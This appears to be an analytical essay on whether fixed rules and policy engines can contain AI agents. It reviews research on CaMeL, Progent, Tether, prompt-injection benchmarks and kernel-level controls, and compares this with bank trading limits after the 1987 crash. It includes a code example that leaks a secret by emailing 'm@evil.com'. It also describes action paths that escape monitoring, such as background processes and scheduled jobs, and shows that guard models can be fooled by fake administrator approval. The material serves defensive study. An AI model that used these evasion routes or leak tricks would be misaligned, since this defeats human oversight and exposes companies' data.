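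- When the agent reads a file: agent's label = max(agent's label, file's label)
- When the agent writes to a file: file's label = max(file's label, agent's label)
- When the agent copies a file: copy's label = original's label

It then allows an upload to an outside site only if the agent's label and the file's label are both "public". The agent needs its own label because it might read a secret and type it into a new file from memory.

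System calls show that a program read one file and then wrote another, but not whether any data passed between them. Tether assumes that it did, which avoids missing a leak but causes some false alarms. For instance, if an agent searches every file on a computer for a word, Tether treats it as having read all the secrets on the machine.

### Checking the rules themselves

An engine that enforces its rules perfectly will also enforce any mistakes in them. For example, AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* describes a rule that limits refunds to "$500 or less", but the code allows only amounts below 500, so the engine would refuse a refund of exactly $500. This mistake does little harm, but it shows how easily a rule can differ from what its author intended, even in a manual.

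Software can find some mistakes before a rule takes effect. The analysis tool for Cedar detects rules that can never apply, such as one that requires a customer to have gold and platinum status at once. It can also compare two versions of a rule. In an example from AWS, a rule allows bulk discounts except on limited-edition products, and someone narrows the exception to limited-edition orders of more than 200 items. An order for 73 limited-edition items, which the old rule excluded, now gets the discount, even though the extra condition seems to make the rule stricter. The tool reports that the new rule is more permissive.

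Sistla and colleagues go further and prove properties of whole sequences of actions. They wrote Tether's rules in Lean, a programming language in which a computer can check mathematical proofs. They proved seven properties for the rules used in their tests. One is that if the agent starts without secret data, no permitted sequence of actions, however long, will bring any into its working memory. These proofs take as given Tether's list of what each command did. The researchers have no such proof for the software that compiles the list from system calls, so they tested it on many generated scripts and fixed the gaps they found.

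None of this can establish that the rules express what the company wants. A logical check could not show whether AWS meant to include $500, because the rule is consistent either way. The problem is worse when a language model translates a company's written policy into code, a feature both AWS and FORGE offer. Palumbo and colleagues warn that the model may leave out a clause or add one that isn't in the policy. They recommend checking that each written requirement has a rule and that each rule is based on a written requirement.

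### Safeguards outside the perimeter

A guard model can take the place of a policy engine and give the same kind of verdict, but its judgement is learned. When Sistla and colleagues tried a commercial guard that uses a language model to review commands, it sometimes gave different verdicts on the same sequence of actions. Some systems mix the two. FORGE, for example, lets a fixed rule use the output of a trained classifier, as in "block the email if the classifier finds confidential data", so the rule is not deterministic.

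Monitoring after the fact does not stop an action. Díaz and colleagues recommend that companies log what an agent reads, which tools it uses and what it produces. Such a log helps a company find faults and improve its rules, but if it shows that the agent emailed the customer list to a stranger, the list has already gone out. The same software can either monitor or enforce. AWS, for example, offers a mode in which its engine records what it would have decided without enforcing the decision. This is a sensible way to try out a new rule, but the rule blocks nothing until the company switches to enforcement.

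Capability thresholds, such as those in the Frontier Safety Framework that Ayoub mentioned, affect how a developer protects and releases a model. Each threshold describes a dangerous ability, such as giving serious help with a cyberattack, and the developer promises extra precautions if a model reaches it. Thresholds do not determine whether an agent may buy a particular chair, and a model far below all of them can still empty a company's bank account. Taneja and Weber make a similar point about the add-ons that agents install, which a registry usually scans before publishing. They compare the scan to a bank's identity check on a new customer, after which the bank still screens every transfer.

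## What fixed rules can and cannot stop

Ayoub's second premise is that a company can build fixed rules around an AI system. This supports his conclusion only if the rules prevent serious harm and still let the agent do its job. Computer scientists worked out much of the theory of such rules decades ago, and since 2025 several teams have measured the results of running agents with and without them.

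### Rules a monitor can enforce

Some monitors can only observe a program's steps and halt the program before a forbidden one. They have a record of what the program has done so far, but not of what it will do next. Schneider proved in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) that such monitors can enforce only safety properties, which are rules of the form "nothing bad has happened so far".

More exactly, a rule is a safety property if every run that breaks it does so at some definite step, and nothing the program does later can repair the breach. Let P be the set of runs that obey the rule, σ a run, and σ[..i] its first i steps. Then:

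if σ ∉ P, there is a step i such that σ[..i]τ ∉ P for every continuation τ.

One of Schneider's examples is a rule against sending any message after reading a file. The monitor only has to record whether the program has read a file. After a read, the monitor halts the program at its first attempt to send a message. A spending cap is also a safety property, because the payment that exceeds the cap is a definite bad step.

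Some rules instead require that something good eventually happen. *CaMeLoT* gives the example of an agent on a company's security team that must get each incident ticket resolved or escalated before it finishes. While a ticket is open, the agent may still deal with it, so a monitor never has grounds to halt the agent. The monitor could refuse to let the agent declare itself finished, but it can't make the agent resolve the ticket. Schneider points out that a time limit can turn such a rule into a safety property, since missing the limit is a definite event. A monitor can then detect the breach, but halting the late agent still leaves the ticket open.

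*CaMeLoT* gets further by checking the plan before the agent acts. It can do this because agents built on the CaMeL design write their whole plan as a short program. *CaMeLoT* converts the plan into a map of every path it could take and checks that each path that opens a ticket also closes it. If one doesn't, the model receives that path as feedback and tries to repair the plan. Schneider's theorem doesn't rule this out, because it covers only monitors that watch a run, not tools that analyse a program in advance. Such a tool can't check an agent that makes up its plan as it goes along, because there is no complete plan to analyse beforehand.

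Schneider also showed that no monitor of this kind can enforce exactly the rule "no secret information leaks out". Whether a message reveals a secret depends partly on what the program would have sent if the secret had been different, and the monitor sees only one run. *The LLMbda Calculus* describes a leak of this sort in CaMeL, which labels data by source and by permitted reader. In outline, the program is:

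```
tmp  = true
rich = true
if balance > threshold:  tmp  = false
if tmp:                  rich = false
if rich:                 send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The program sends the email only if the customer's balance is above the threshold, so the email reveals that the secret balance is high. When the balance is high, the program skips the line that would have changed the variable "rich". CaMeL labels data based only on the lines that run, so "rich" still counts as public and the email passes the check.

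Schneider notes that monitors against leaks work by enforcing a stricter rule than the one the company wants. This is why FORGE, the system that traces which earlier events may have influenced an action, sometimes blocks a harmless email. A rule strict enough to catch every leak will also cause some false alarms.

### What changes with AI agents

Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, extends this theory to agents, which differ from the older programs in four ways. Some rules depend on judgements that software gets wrong, such as whether an email contains personal data. Many actions, such as payments, are irreversible. The data in an action can vary without limit, so nobody can list every possible recipient and amount in advance. Outside content can also steer what the agent proposes. Ray gives each result its own assumptions and does not claim that one theorem covers all four differences.

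Ray's example is an assistant that handles email and payments under three rules. It must never email personal data to anyone outside an approved list, never transfer more than a set sum to any one recipient in a day, and never send anything after the user withdraws its access. A gate, Ray's word for a check that runs before each action, can apply the last two rules using reliable records. To apply the first, it needs a judge to read the email, and the judge may be wrong.

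The main theorem gives the exact conditions under which a gate can stop every violation without ever interfering with an agent that is obeying the rule. The rule must be a safety property, and the gate's memory must be good enough to tell whether the actions so far comply. The theorem assumes that the gate always gets correct answers to questions such as "does this contain personal data?"

Irreversibility prevents Ray's gate from holding an action back until later, as some other monitors can. Under the rule "every payment is eventually followed by a confirmation", such a monitor could delay the payment until the confirmation arrives, then release both. Ray's gate has to decide when the agent proposes the payment. If it allows the payment, the confirmation may never come, but if it blocks the payment, it may obstruct an agent that was about to confirm.

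"Certified" in Ray's subtitle can mean that the gate enforces the rule on every sequence of actions, provided the answers it receives are correct. It can also mean that the average risk has a statistical limit, provided the violations used to tune the judge resemble those it will meet in use. Neither meaning guarantees that everything the agent does will be safe.

A statistical certificate can be useless, because a gate that blocks everything satisfies it. Ray tuned 23 judges on 132 short instructions, some harmless and some malicious. When the target was to miss at most 5% of violations, every tuned judge blocked everything. With a 10% target, one judge, Google's small model Gemma 2 9B, missed only 1% of violations but blocked 78% of the harmless instructions.

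Ray also found that if rules can use two counters that go down as well as up, no program can always work out whether a given set of rules will ever block anything. Daily caps and withdrawals of access avoid this problem because their counters only go up. This gives companies a reason to keep their rules simple if they want to check them in advance.

### Attacks stopped and tasks lost

Most tests of perimeter designs use AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office work. It has 97 ordinary tasks in four settings: a workplace account with email and files, the chat service Slack, banking and travel. Combining the tasks with hidden malicious instructions gives 629 attack cases. Researchers count how many ordinary tasks an agent completes and how many attacks succeed.

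Progent, which checks each tool call against a list of permissions, made attacks much less likely to succeed. Shi and colleagues tested it with OpenAI's GPT-4o as both the agent and the model that writes the permissions. The share of successful attacks fell from 39.9% to 1.0% on the AgentDojo benchmark and from 70.3% to 3.9% on another, Agent Security Bench. The agent completed about as many tasks as it did without Progent. These tests put Progent at a disadvantage because the researchers automatically approved every request for wider permissions. When a person reviewed the permissions instead, no attack on AgentDojo succeeded.

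Most of the remaining failures on Agent Security Bench involved malicious tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled legitimate ones. The checker enforced its rules correctly, but the model that wrote the rules had permitted the wrong tool. Hand-written rules brought the failure rate to zero. *Bounded Agents* (2026) reports a separate run of Progent with hand-written rules in which no attack succeeded in any setting tested.

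CaMeL usually leaves more tasks unfinished. *ConfGuard* (Arunkumar, Gangadharan and Senthilkumar, 2026) cites the best-known figure, that CaMeL solves 77% of AgentDojo's tasks. *SecureClaw* (Ma and Schmid, 2026) measured 70% for an undefended agent running on GPT-4o mini. The figures come from different studies, so comparing them does not show how CaMeL affects task completion.

Two studies measured the effect of CaMeL's data policies more clearly by running it with them on and off. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) tested CaMeL on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks. With Claude Opus 4.7, it solved 15 tasks with the policies off and 5 with them on. With three other models, it solved 13 to 17 with the policies off and 4 to 6 with them on. *The LLMbda Calculus* found that turning the policies on halved CaMeL's success in the banking setting.

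So the 77% figure is a poor guide to what a particular company would lose, because the loss depends on the model, the policies and the work. Compared with an undefended agent, Ma and Schmid's own design, for instance, cut the share of attacks that got through from 31.5% to 0.6% and the share of ordinary tasks completed from 70% to 61%. A company might accept that loss for an agent that makes payments, but probably not for one that tidies calendars.

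Fixed rules are less useful for newer models, which resist more attacks without them. *aiAuthZ* (2026) tested two 2026 models in the banking setting with a standard attack, using 20 cases per condition. No attack succeeded, even without a defence. Adding a strict list of permitted payees did more harm than good in this test. The list blocked seven calls that served the attacker, but it also reduced success on ordinary tasks from 100% to 80% by blocking a legitimate first payment to someone new.

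The rules are still necessary even with better models. The attack was a standard one, and Gray Swan's attacker, which learned from its failures, did much better against recent models than fixed lists of attacks did. A rule matters most on the rare occasion when the model gives in. But there is little evidence about how well rules hold up against attackers who study them. Toyoda, Leung and Bhuvaneswari (2026), in *guardscope*, found only one published test of this kind against a rule-based monitor. The monitor, Progent, held up, but the test used a single attack template.

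AgentDojo's tasks may also make the defences look better than they are. *AgentDyn* (2026) tested five defences, not all of them rule-based, on AgentDojo and on a new set of tasks that change more as the agent works. Under attack, undefended GPT-4o completed about half the tasks in each set. Most of the defended agents completed more than half on AgentDojo, but on the new tasks every defended GPT-4o agent completed considerably fewer than the undefended one.

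### Gates that raised task success

Fixed rules do not always reduce the amount of work an AI completes. Reddy, Challaram and Basu (2026), in *Reason Less, Verify More*, studied an agent that handles customer service for a simulated airline. The agent has written instructions about which bookings it may cancel or change, but the booking software carries out any properly formatted request, even if those instructions forbid it. With GPT-4o mini as the agent, 78% of the failures were silent, meaning that the final booking record was wrong but no tool had returned an error.

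The researchers added four gates, each a short piece of code that compares a proposed change with the airline's database. One blocks cancellations that the fare rules forbid, and another blocks any change to the number of passengers. A third checks baggage charges, and the fourth requires the agent to read a record before editing it. If a gate blocks a change, it returns a reason, and the agent can try something else.

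With gates, the agent's success rate across 50 tasks with five attempts each rose from 29.6% to 42.0%. In a repeat with 15 new attempts per task, it rose by almost the same amount, from 30.8% to 43.1%. The agent also became more consistent, completing 26% of the tasks on all five attempts, up from 8% without gates. GPT-5.2, a stronger model, improved from 61.2% to 71.6%, though nobody has repeated that run.

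In one task that shows why a rule outside the model can help, a customer gives false information to get a cancellation the airline doesn't allow. Agents without the gates handled this correctly at most once in 16 attempts, while agents with them succeeded in all 16. The gate allows or blocks the cancellation based on the booking record, so it makes no difference how convincing the customer is.

However, almost all of the gain came from the cancellation gate. Reddy and colleagues checked each refusal against the correct solution, with very uneven results:

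| Gate | Times it blocked a change | Correct blocks | Share correct |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cancellation rules | 161 | 161 | 100% |
| Passenger numbers | 9 | 9 | 100% |
| Read before editing | 90 | 70 | 78% |
| Baggage charges | 42 | 2 | 5% |

The baggage gate was as deterministic as the others, but it was wrong 40 times out of 42. A company can predict what a deterministic gate will do and still have written the wrong rule, so it needs to check the gate's refusals against decisions it knows are right.

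The gates failed in other ways too. In one task, the agent kept running into a refusal and never found a permitted solution. GPT-5.2 did worse than before on three tasks where gates intervened. In a simulated shop whose software already refused forbidden changes, gates added no benefit, and the success rate fell slightly, from 62.5% to 57.8%, mostly because a programming error blocked valid corrections. The researchers also set their gates to let a request through if the gate crashed. This avoids needless interruptions, but a company guarding against theft would want a crashed gate to block requests.

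This evidence comes from one simulated airline, and the researchers wrote the gates with the test tasks in mind. But it is still good evidence that a few lines of code can make an agent both safer and more useful when a rule depends only on facts in a database and the existing software doesn't enforce it.

### Actions that never reach the checkpoint

All these results depend on an action passing through the check. To examine how often that happens, Toyoda and colleagues listed 15 paths by which an agent can affect a computer or network, including calling a remote tool, starting another program, opening an internet connection directly, and scheduling a job for later. They worked out which of these paths a control can check from each of several positions.

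One position is a gateway between the agent and its remote tools. Another is inside the agent's own software, where Toyoda and colleagues place Progent, CaMeL and FORGE. A third is the kernel, the core of the operating system, which programs have to go through to open a file or a network connection. Their analysis gives these counts:

| Position of the control | Paths checked | Blocked by other means | Depends on the set-up | Unchecked |
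|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gateway, with open internet access | 1 | 0 | 3 | 11 |
| Gateway for all tools, with other internet access blocked | 3 | 1 | 4 | 7 |
| Inside the agent's software | 5 | 0 | 1 | 9 |
| Kernel | 13 | 0 | 1 | 1 |

No control outside the kernel covers five of the paths an agent can use to act. For example, an agent may start a background program that keeps running after the approved command has finished, or hand a job to the computer's scheduler. Combining a gateway with a check inside the agent's software doesn't block these paths, because the actions pass through neither. Most of the products Toyoda and colleagues classified are in the positions with narrower coverage.

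The kernel checks the most paths but has the least information about them. It can record that a program opened a certain file, but not which tool call or conversation led to that. A rule such as "refund only the customer in this conversation" therefore has to be enforced outside the kernel.

Toyoda and colleagues tested part of this analysis with real products, using 15 actions across four of the paths. A gateway combined with the agent's own permission checks checked all seven tool calls and none of the other eight actions. ActPlane, a kernel product, checked seven of those eight actions, missing one network message. It checked none of the tool calls, although a kernel control could in principle do so. By these counts, the two arrangements together would have missed one action in 15. Coverage of the other 11 paths rests on analysis alone.

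Full coverage means only that every action is checked against a rule. The study did not test whether the rules produced correct decisions. A control that applied the airline's baggage rule to all 15 paths would have full coverage but be wrong on every path.

### Reading a document, then sending an email

Díaz and colleagues, security specialists at Google, raise the more basic objection that fixed rules often lack the context to distinguish good actions from bad ones. For example, when an agent reads a document and then sends an email, the email may be a summary the user requested or a leak.

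"No sending after reading a file" is Schneider's example of an enforceable rule, and a monitor needs only two states to apply it. But the rule blocks the summary as well as the leak, and without it both go out. Díaz and colleagues add that writing rules for everything a general-purpose agent might do is complex and hard to scale, so some rules will block legitimate work and others will allow harm that their writers did not foresee.

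CaMeL's lists of permitted readers partly answer the objection, because a rule can check each recipient against them. But somebody has to keep the lists accurate, and some decisions still take judgement. If a manager wants to send an outsider a two-line summary of a confidential report while keeping the figures private, somebody has to decide whether the summary gives too much away.

Google combines a layer of policy engines with a layer of model-based defences. The second layer uses guard models and training on examples of attacks, and another model may estimate whether a plan is likely to end badly. Díaz and colleagues consider neither layer sufficient alone.

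Whether the hybrid still counts as a deterministic perimeter depends on how a company connects the layers. Let R be the set of actions that the fixed rules allow, and G the set that a guard model allows on a given occasion. If an action needs approval from both, the agent can take only the actions in

R ∩ G ⊆ R.

The agent can never go beyond R, even if G changes from one day to the next. Such a system has a deterministic outer boundary and a less predictable filter inside it. Google's suggestion that a worrying prediction could trigger stricter enforcement fits this pattern.

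The company loses that boundary if a model's output can also relax a rule, as with FORGE's classifier-based rules, because fooling the classifier can then allow an action the rule would have blocked. Letting a person approve exceptions has a similar effect. For example, one of Google's sample rules stops an agent from emailing outsiders after it has read data from a suspicious source, unless the user explicitly approves.

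Even in the stricter arrangement, a company can promise only what R guarantees. If R allows external email because staff need it, only the guard model can stop a confidential document from being sent to a stranger. The hybrid protects better than rules alone, but its protection in the read-then-send case is still non-deterministic.

Guard models can also reduce how much work an agent completes. Ray ran a small agent through 949 AgentDojo episodes with a small model judging each action. Successful attacks fell from 45 to 4, but the judge blocked 78% of the agent's calls, and task success fell from 25% to 18%. A more lenient judge blocked 12% of calls, but 30 attacks succeeded. Blocking also changed what the agent tried next. In a paired comparison of 389 episodes, the stricter judge prevented 34 attacks that had succeeded without it, but five others succeeded only when it was present.

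Such judges can also be fooled. When Ray added a short false claim of an administrator's approval to the text they read, the share of violations missed rose by 20 to 60 percentage points for 8 of 11 judges. The judges were mostly small models, and stronger ones may do better, as the browsing results for Claude Opus 5 suggest. A false claim of approval does not affect a spending cap, because the cap does not depend on the text.

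### Harms within and beyond the rules' reach

Fixed rules work best when software can check the size or destination of a harm. If a rules engine limits an agent to $500 a day and every payment goes through the engine, the agent can lose at most $15,000 in 30 days, even if an attacker fully controls it. A company with ten such agents could lose up to $150,000 in that time, but it can calculate this maximum before switching them on, which it can't do by testing a model's behaviour.

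Limits on destinations work similarly. A list of approved payees prevents an agent from paying a stranger, but it also delays some legitimate first payments. Ma and Schmid's system also ties each approval to the exact request, including its recipient. If a compromised agent changes the recipient afterwards, the approval no longer matches and the software blocks the request.

Deletions are also fairly easy to contain. A company can deny the agent permission to delete anything, or require a person to confirm each deletion. The rule needs to cover overwriting too, since an agent that replaces a customer database with an empty file has destroyed the data without deleting the database. It is probably safest to keep backups where the agent has no access, so that the company can recover its data if the rule has a mistake.

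This kind of protection doesn't stop an agent from giving bad advice. An agent that wrongly tells a customer that a policy covers flood damage has only produced text, so there may be no tool call to check. Shi and colleagues state that Progent doesn't address attacks that affect only an agent's written output. A company could forbid the agent to discuss insurance, but then it couldn't use the agent to answer insurance questions.

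Subtly wrong work is similar, except that the agent does use its tools. It may save a budget with a faulty formula or add a flaw to a program, and a rule about file access won't block either change because the agent was supposed to edit that file. Ma and Schmid say their policies may allow an action the user didn't intend. The damage may come weeks later, when somebody relies on the budget.

A rule can catch some of these errors if it can check them against an independent fact. Arunkumar and colleagues consider an agent that schedules engine maintenance. If it reports that a healthy engine has three cycles of use left, an ordinary permission check will accept the report, because the agent is allowed to file it and the data came from an approved source. Their system therefore adds a rule from physics: an engine's remaining life never rises, and it falls by at most one cycle per cycle of use.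 In tests on NASA engine data, this cut a covert attacker's reach on healthy engines from 52.9% to 4.6%, while sending 2.7% of normal readings to a person. But the rule protects only the decision about how urgent the maintenance is. The system did not stop an injected instruction that changed only other parts of the work order.

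## What banks did about computer trading, 1987 to 1996

Ayoub's third premise is that banks restricted trading algorithms with fixed rules in the late 1980s and early 1990s. He named no bank or rule, so checking the claim means looking for an episode that fits. The obvious place to start is the stock market crash of October 1987, which many people blamed on computer trading. Exchanges, brokerage firms, banks and supervisors all tightened their controls over the next nine years, but for different reasons, and often the controls had little to do with computers.

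### Program trading and portfolio insurance

The New York Stock Exchange counted an order as a program trade if it covered at least 15 stocks worth a total of $1 million or more. The economist Peter Fortune (1993) pointed out in the Boston Federal Reserve's *New England Economic Review* that this definition has no reference to computers. Traders usually sent such orders through SuperDot, the exchange's electronic order system. Carlson (2006), in *A Brief History of the 1987 Stock Market Crash*, describes computers set up to trade many stocks quickly when certain conditions were met.

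One of the two main strategies was portfolio insurance, which was supposed to let a pension fund profit from rising share prices without ever falling below a chosen floor. In a simplified version, the fund follows the rule

money in stocks = 5 × (value of the portfolio − floor)

and keeps the rest in cash. Suppose the portfolio is worth $110 million and the floor is $100 million. The fund holds $50 million in stocks and $60 million in cash. If share prices drop by 10%, the fund loses $5 million and is now only $5 million above its floor. The rule allows it $25 million in stocks, but it still has $45 million, so it must sell $20 million. If prices drop again, it must sell again. The floor holds only if the fund can sell before prices have dropped by more than a fifth.

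The models in real use were more elaborate but had the same effect. Most portfolio insurers also sold index futures rather than shares. These contracts, whose value follows a share index such as the S&P 500, were cheaper and quicker to trade.

The other strategy, index arbitrage, made money from gaps between the prices of the futures and the shares. If the futures were cheaper, a trader bought them and sold the shares, which pushed the two prices back together.

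Portfolio insurance was itself a fixed rule that people had adopted for safety. Anyone who knew the formula and the portfolio's value could calculate the next order. The rule's weakness was that it made no allowance for a lack of buyers.

### The crash of October 1987

On Monday 19 October 1987 the Dow Jones Industrial Average, an index of 30 large American companies, fell by 508 points, or 22.6%. President Reagan asked a commission under the banker Nicholas Brady to find out why. The Brady report, as it is now known (Presidential Task Force on Market Mechanisms, 1988), traced the fall to bad trade figures and a proposed tax on takeovers, which had pushed prices down since the previous Wednesday. That decline caused portfolio insurers to sell futures. Index arbitrageurs then bought the cheap futures and sold shares, which spread the fall from Chicago's futures market to the stock exchange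 in New York, and the lower share prices led the insurers to sell more futures.

By Friday evening the insurers should have sold at least $12 billion under their models, but they had sold less than $4 billion. Other traders could see that more sales were coming and sold first. On Monday, portfolio insurers sold futures equivalent to about $4 billion of stock, over 40% of futures volume excluding trades that involved the market's own floor traders. Three insurers also sold nearly $2 billion of shares in New York. One large investor sold 13 batches of shares worth almost $100 million each. These sales were still a small fraction of what the models required.

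In *The October Crash*, an analysis for the Federal Reserve Bank of St. Louis, Santoni (1988) called this account the "cascade theory" and found several problems with it. At about 1:30 on Monday afternoon, futures were some 15 points cheaper than the shares in the index. A contract was worth $500 times the index, so an insurer who sold futures instead of shares got about $7,500 less per contract. Santoni doubted that sophisticated investors would do that. The Brady report gives a fairly good answer, which is that several major insurers were allowed to trade only futures, not their clients' shares.

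Santoni's other objections are harder to answer. Index arbitrage had almost stopped by early afternoon, yet the Dow fell more than 300 points after that. The Brady task force argued that the arbitrage stopped too early, so futures dropped far below shares and the gap scared off potential share buyers. But markets abroad with hardly any program trading crashed too. Roll (1988), in *The International Crash of October 1987*, found that 19 of 23 national markets fell by more than 20% that month, and that the American decline was the fifth smallest in local currency. In simple comparisons between countries, markets with computer-directed trading tended to fall less.

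Fortune mostly blamed the stock exchange's inability to process the orders. The printers on the trading floor ran up to 75 minutes late, so investors didn't know what price they were getting or whether they had sold at all, and many decided to get out of the market. Official bodies also disagreed. According to Carlson, the Securities and Exchange Commission (SEC), which regulates American stock markets, thought portfolio insurance had done harm in several ways, while the acting head of the futures regulator said the trading data did not match the cascade theory. Congress's audit office, the GAO, blamed a combination of economic, political, psychological and trading factors in *Financial Markets* (1988).

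Markets fell worldwide, so American trading programs are unlikely to have caused the crash, though they probably made it faster in the United States. More important for Ayoub's analogy, neither side claimed that the programs had departed from their instructions. Their owners had set them to sell when prices fell, and the trouble came from many owners giving the same instruction.

### What the exchanges did

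The first control came the next morning. The Brady task force wrote that the NYSE prohibited brokers from using its order system for index arbitrage on their own account. According to a trade newsletter, WatersTechnology's *Trading Technology At The Crossroads*, the exchange "asked" its members to refrain. Either way, the control reduced index arbitrage selling. Among the large institutions that the task force tracked, these sales fell from $1,774 million on Monday to $128 million on Tuesday.

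In protecting its own market, the exchange also hurt the futures market in Chicago. When futures are cheap, arbitrageurs buy them and sell shares at the same time, but on Tuesday those buyers were missing. The main futures contract fell by 27% between 10:00 and 12:15, and the task force thought the lack of arbitrage contributed greatly to the fall.

At 12:15 the Chicago exchange halted trading in futures, and the Dow gained 125 points in 45 minutes. When futures trading resumed, the Dow lost almost 100 points in half an hour. The Brady task force took this as a sign that the halt had helped by cutting most portfolio insurers off from the market. Fortune wrote that the halt and the restriction on SuperDot were probably mistakes, since they made it harder for investors to trade and to find out what was going on.

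Fixed rules followed. According to Santoni, from 4 February 1988 the NYSE denied program traders the use of its order system whenever the Dow had moved more than 50 points from the previous day's close. In October 1988 the exchanges adopted a fuller set of "circuit breakers", which they amended in 1990. Fortune lists the New York rules as they then stood:

| Rule | Trigger | Effect |
|---|---|---|
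| 80A | S&P 500 futures fall 12 points | Program orders sent through SuperDot wait five minutes |
| 80A | Dow moves 50 points up or down | Index arbitrageurs may not sell just after a price has fallen, or buy just after it has risen |
| 80B | Dow falls 250 points | All trading stops for one hour |
| 80B | Dow falls 400 points | All trading stops for two hours |

These rules come closer than anything else from the period to what Ayoub described. They are deterministic, sit outside the trading programs, and apply whatever the reason for a trade. At least part of the industry disliked most of them. In February 1990 the exchange proposed the restriction on index arbitrage in the table's second row. Most of those who wrote to the SEC about it asked the agency to reject it, according to WatersTechnology's *Proposed Curbs On Programs Meet Opposition*.

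The rules had gaps. The five-minute delay applied only to orders sent through SuperDot, so a firm could avoid it by having brokers carry the same order across the floor by hand. The delay therefore didn't meet Anderson's requirement that a program should never be able to go around the check. The triggers also became considerably stricter without anyone changing them, because the exchange had set them in points and share prices kept rising. Fortune calculated that a 250-point fall was a drop of 11.6% in October 1988 but only about 7.5% by early 1993.

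It is hard to say how well the rules worked. By 1993 no fall had been large enough to trigger Rule 80B. On 13 October 1989 the Dow fell 190 points even though circuit breakers interrupted futures trading twice. On 23 July 1990 a 16-minute halt in futures came just before a rebound that lasted into the next day. Prices might have moved the same way on both days without the halts. The evidence on Rule 80A is better. *Another Day, Another Collar* (1997), a working paper from the US Treasury's bank regulator, found that the rule sharply reduced index arbitrage. The stock and futures markets stayed linked, though gaps between their prices took longer to close. The exchange dropped the restriction in 2007 after concluding that it neither restrained nor increased volatility, according to Finextra's *NYSE drops curbs on program trading*.

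### What the brokerage firms did

Some firms curbed their program trading on their own. In the last week of October 1989, two weeks after the 190-point fall, Morgan Stanley, Bear Stearns and Oppenheimer announced that they would stop index arbitrage with their own money, at least for a while, but continue it for clients. Paine Webber, which had stopped it for its own account in May 1988, now stopped it for clients too. The Los Angeles Times' *3 Major Brokerages to Curb Program Trading Activity* adds that Goldman Sachs had given up program trading for its own account after the 1987 crash, and that Dean Witter Reynolds had abandoned it earlier in 1989.

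This was a real change, since Morgan Stanley and Bear Stearns were among the four largest index arbitrageurs on the exchange that September. But the firms seem to have been responding to complaints from clients and stockbrokers rather than to worries about losing control of their programs. Kemper, a large money manager in Chicago, had told several of them that it would take its business elsewhere as long as they used the strategy for themselves. Their own stockbrokers were complaining that wild markets drove customers away. James Cayne, the president of Bear Stearns, said that many major clients felt the firm shouldn't use the strategy.

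The firms stopped using the programs to trade their own money but kept running them for clients, without building a fence around them. A program presumably had the same effect on the market whether it traded Morgan Stanley's money or a client's. A company that followed this example with AI would forbid agents in some departments and leave them alone in others. That can be sensible, but it doesn't show that anyone knows how to contain an agent while it works.

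### Limits on trading desks

Large commercial banks did build something like a fence around their trading businesses. According to *Red-Blooded Risk*, a history of Wall Street risk management, the effort began in late 1989 or early 1990, when the 1987 crash was "ancient history" and bankers were worried about a run of scandals and bankruptcies that had done damage far beyond the firms involved. JPMorgan and Bankers Trust felt the problem most, because they competed with investment banks in most businesses, and Citibank was nervous about its currency trading. The people in charge wanted a way to control trading businesses "they didn't understand".

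That is remarkably close to Ayoub's description of companies and AI. But what the bankers did not understand was desks full of human traders.

The simplest tool for this is a position limit, which caps how much of something a desk may hold, for example $50 million of yen. It is as deterministic as a spending cap, provided the bank records every trade. A loss limit, which is nearly as simple, requires a desk to cut its positions once it has lost a certain sum, but the loss may still grow. A desk with $20 million of American shares and a $2 million loss limit could have lost about $4 million on 19 October 1987 if it found no buyers that day.

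Neither limit lets a bank's chairman compare a yen desk with a bond desk, or add the two together. Value at risk does. It is the loss that a portfolio should not exceed over a set period with a set probability. If daily gains and losses follow a bell curve around zero, then

value at risk = *z* × *σ* × *V*,

where *V* is the value of the portfolio, *σ* is its volatility (the standard deviation of its daily returns), and *z* depends on the chosen probability. For 99%, *z* is 2.326. A $100 million portfolio with a daily volatility of 1% therefore has a value at risk of

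2.326 × 0.01 × $100 million ≈ $2.33 million.

The bank should expect to lose more than that on about one trading day in a hundred, or two or three days a year.

To combine two desks, the bank also needs the correlation between them, *ρ*, which is 1 if they always gain and lose together and 0 if they are unrelated:

total = √(*A*² + *B*² + 2*ρAB*),

where *A* and *B* are the two desks' values at risk. Two desks at $2.33 million each come to $3.29 million if they are unrelated and $4.65 million if they move together. At JPMorgan the chairman, Dennis Weatherstone, had a one-page summary of the whole bank's risk on his desk at 4:15 every afternoon. The bank published its method in 1994 under the name RiskMetrics, and value at risk spread quickly.

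### A fixed limit on an estimated number

A bank might tell a desk to keep its value at risk below $3 million. That limit is less firm than a limit on yen, because the bank can count its yen but has to estimate volatility, and there are several reasonable ways to do that.

Take the $100 million portfolio again, with a volatility of 1%, on a day when it loses 4%. It is now worth $96 million. One bank calculates volatility from the last 250 trading days and gives each the same weight. The bad day barely changes its estimate, which goes from 1% to about 1.03%, and the desk's value at risk is $2.30 million. Another bank uses the RiskMetrics formula for daily data,

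new *σ*² = 0.94 × old *σ*² + 0.06 × (latest return)²,

which gives recent days much more weight. Its estimate jumps to about 1.38%, and value at risk comes to $3.08 million. The portfolios are identical and so are the limits, but the second desk has to sell and the first doesn't.

A value-at-risk limit is only partly deterministic. Each bank's calculation is still deterministic, but the bank can't know in advance whether the result is right. A limit on yen guarantees that the desk holds no more than $50 million of yen, while a limit on value at risk guarantees only that a formula produces a number below $3 million. The actual risk, which the bank cares about most, may be much greater.

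The difference can be large, as it was in October 1987. Fortune estimated the daily volatility of the S&P 500 from January to early October that year at 0.92%. For $100 million of shares in the index, that gives a value at risk of $2.14 million. On 19 October such a portfolio lost about $20.5 million, more than nine times as much. The estimate allows for a larger loss on one day in a hundred and doesn't predict how much larger, so this loss does not contradict it. But if returns followed a bell curve with that volatility, a loss of this size would practically never happen.

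Like portfolio insurance, a value-at-risk limit can force desks to sell when markets fall sharply, because estimates of volatility rise and desks near their limits exceed them. The second desk above would need to sell only about $2.4 million of shares to bring its value at risk back under $3 million, which is trivial for one desk. Such sales would matter more if most large banks used similar formulas and limits.

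### What the supervisors did

Bank supervisors turned these habits into official expectations. In December 1993 the Federal Reserve sent its examiners guidance on how to judge a bank's trading activities. Under the guidance, a bank's board should approve its policies on trading risk, the people who measure the risk should be independent of the people who take it, and the bank should have a system of limits and a procedure for dealing with breaches. The guidance covered trading in general, especially the growing business in derivatives, rather than computer programs. Much of it concerned who reports to whom, which is sensible but can't be turned into a rule that software applies to an order.

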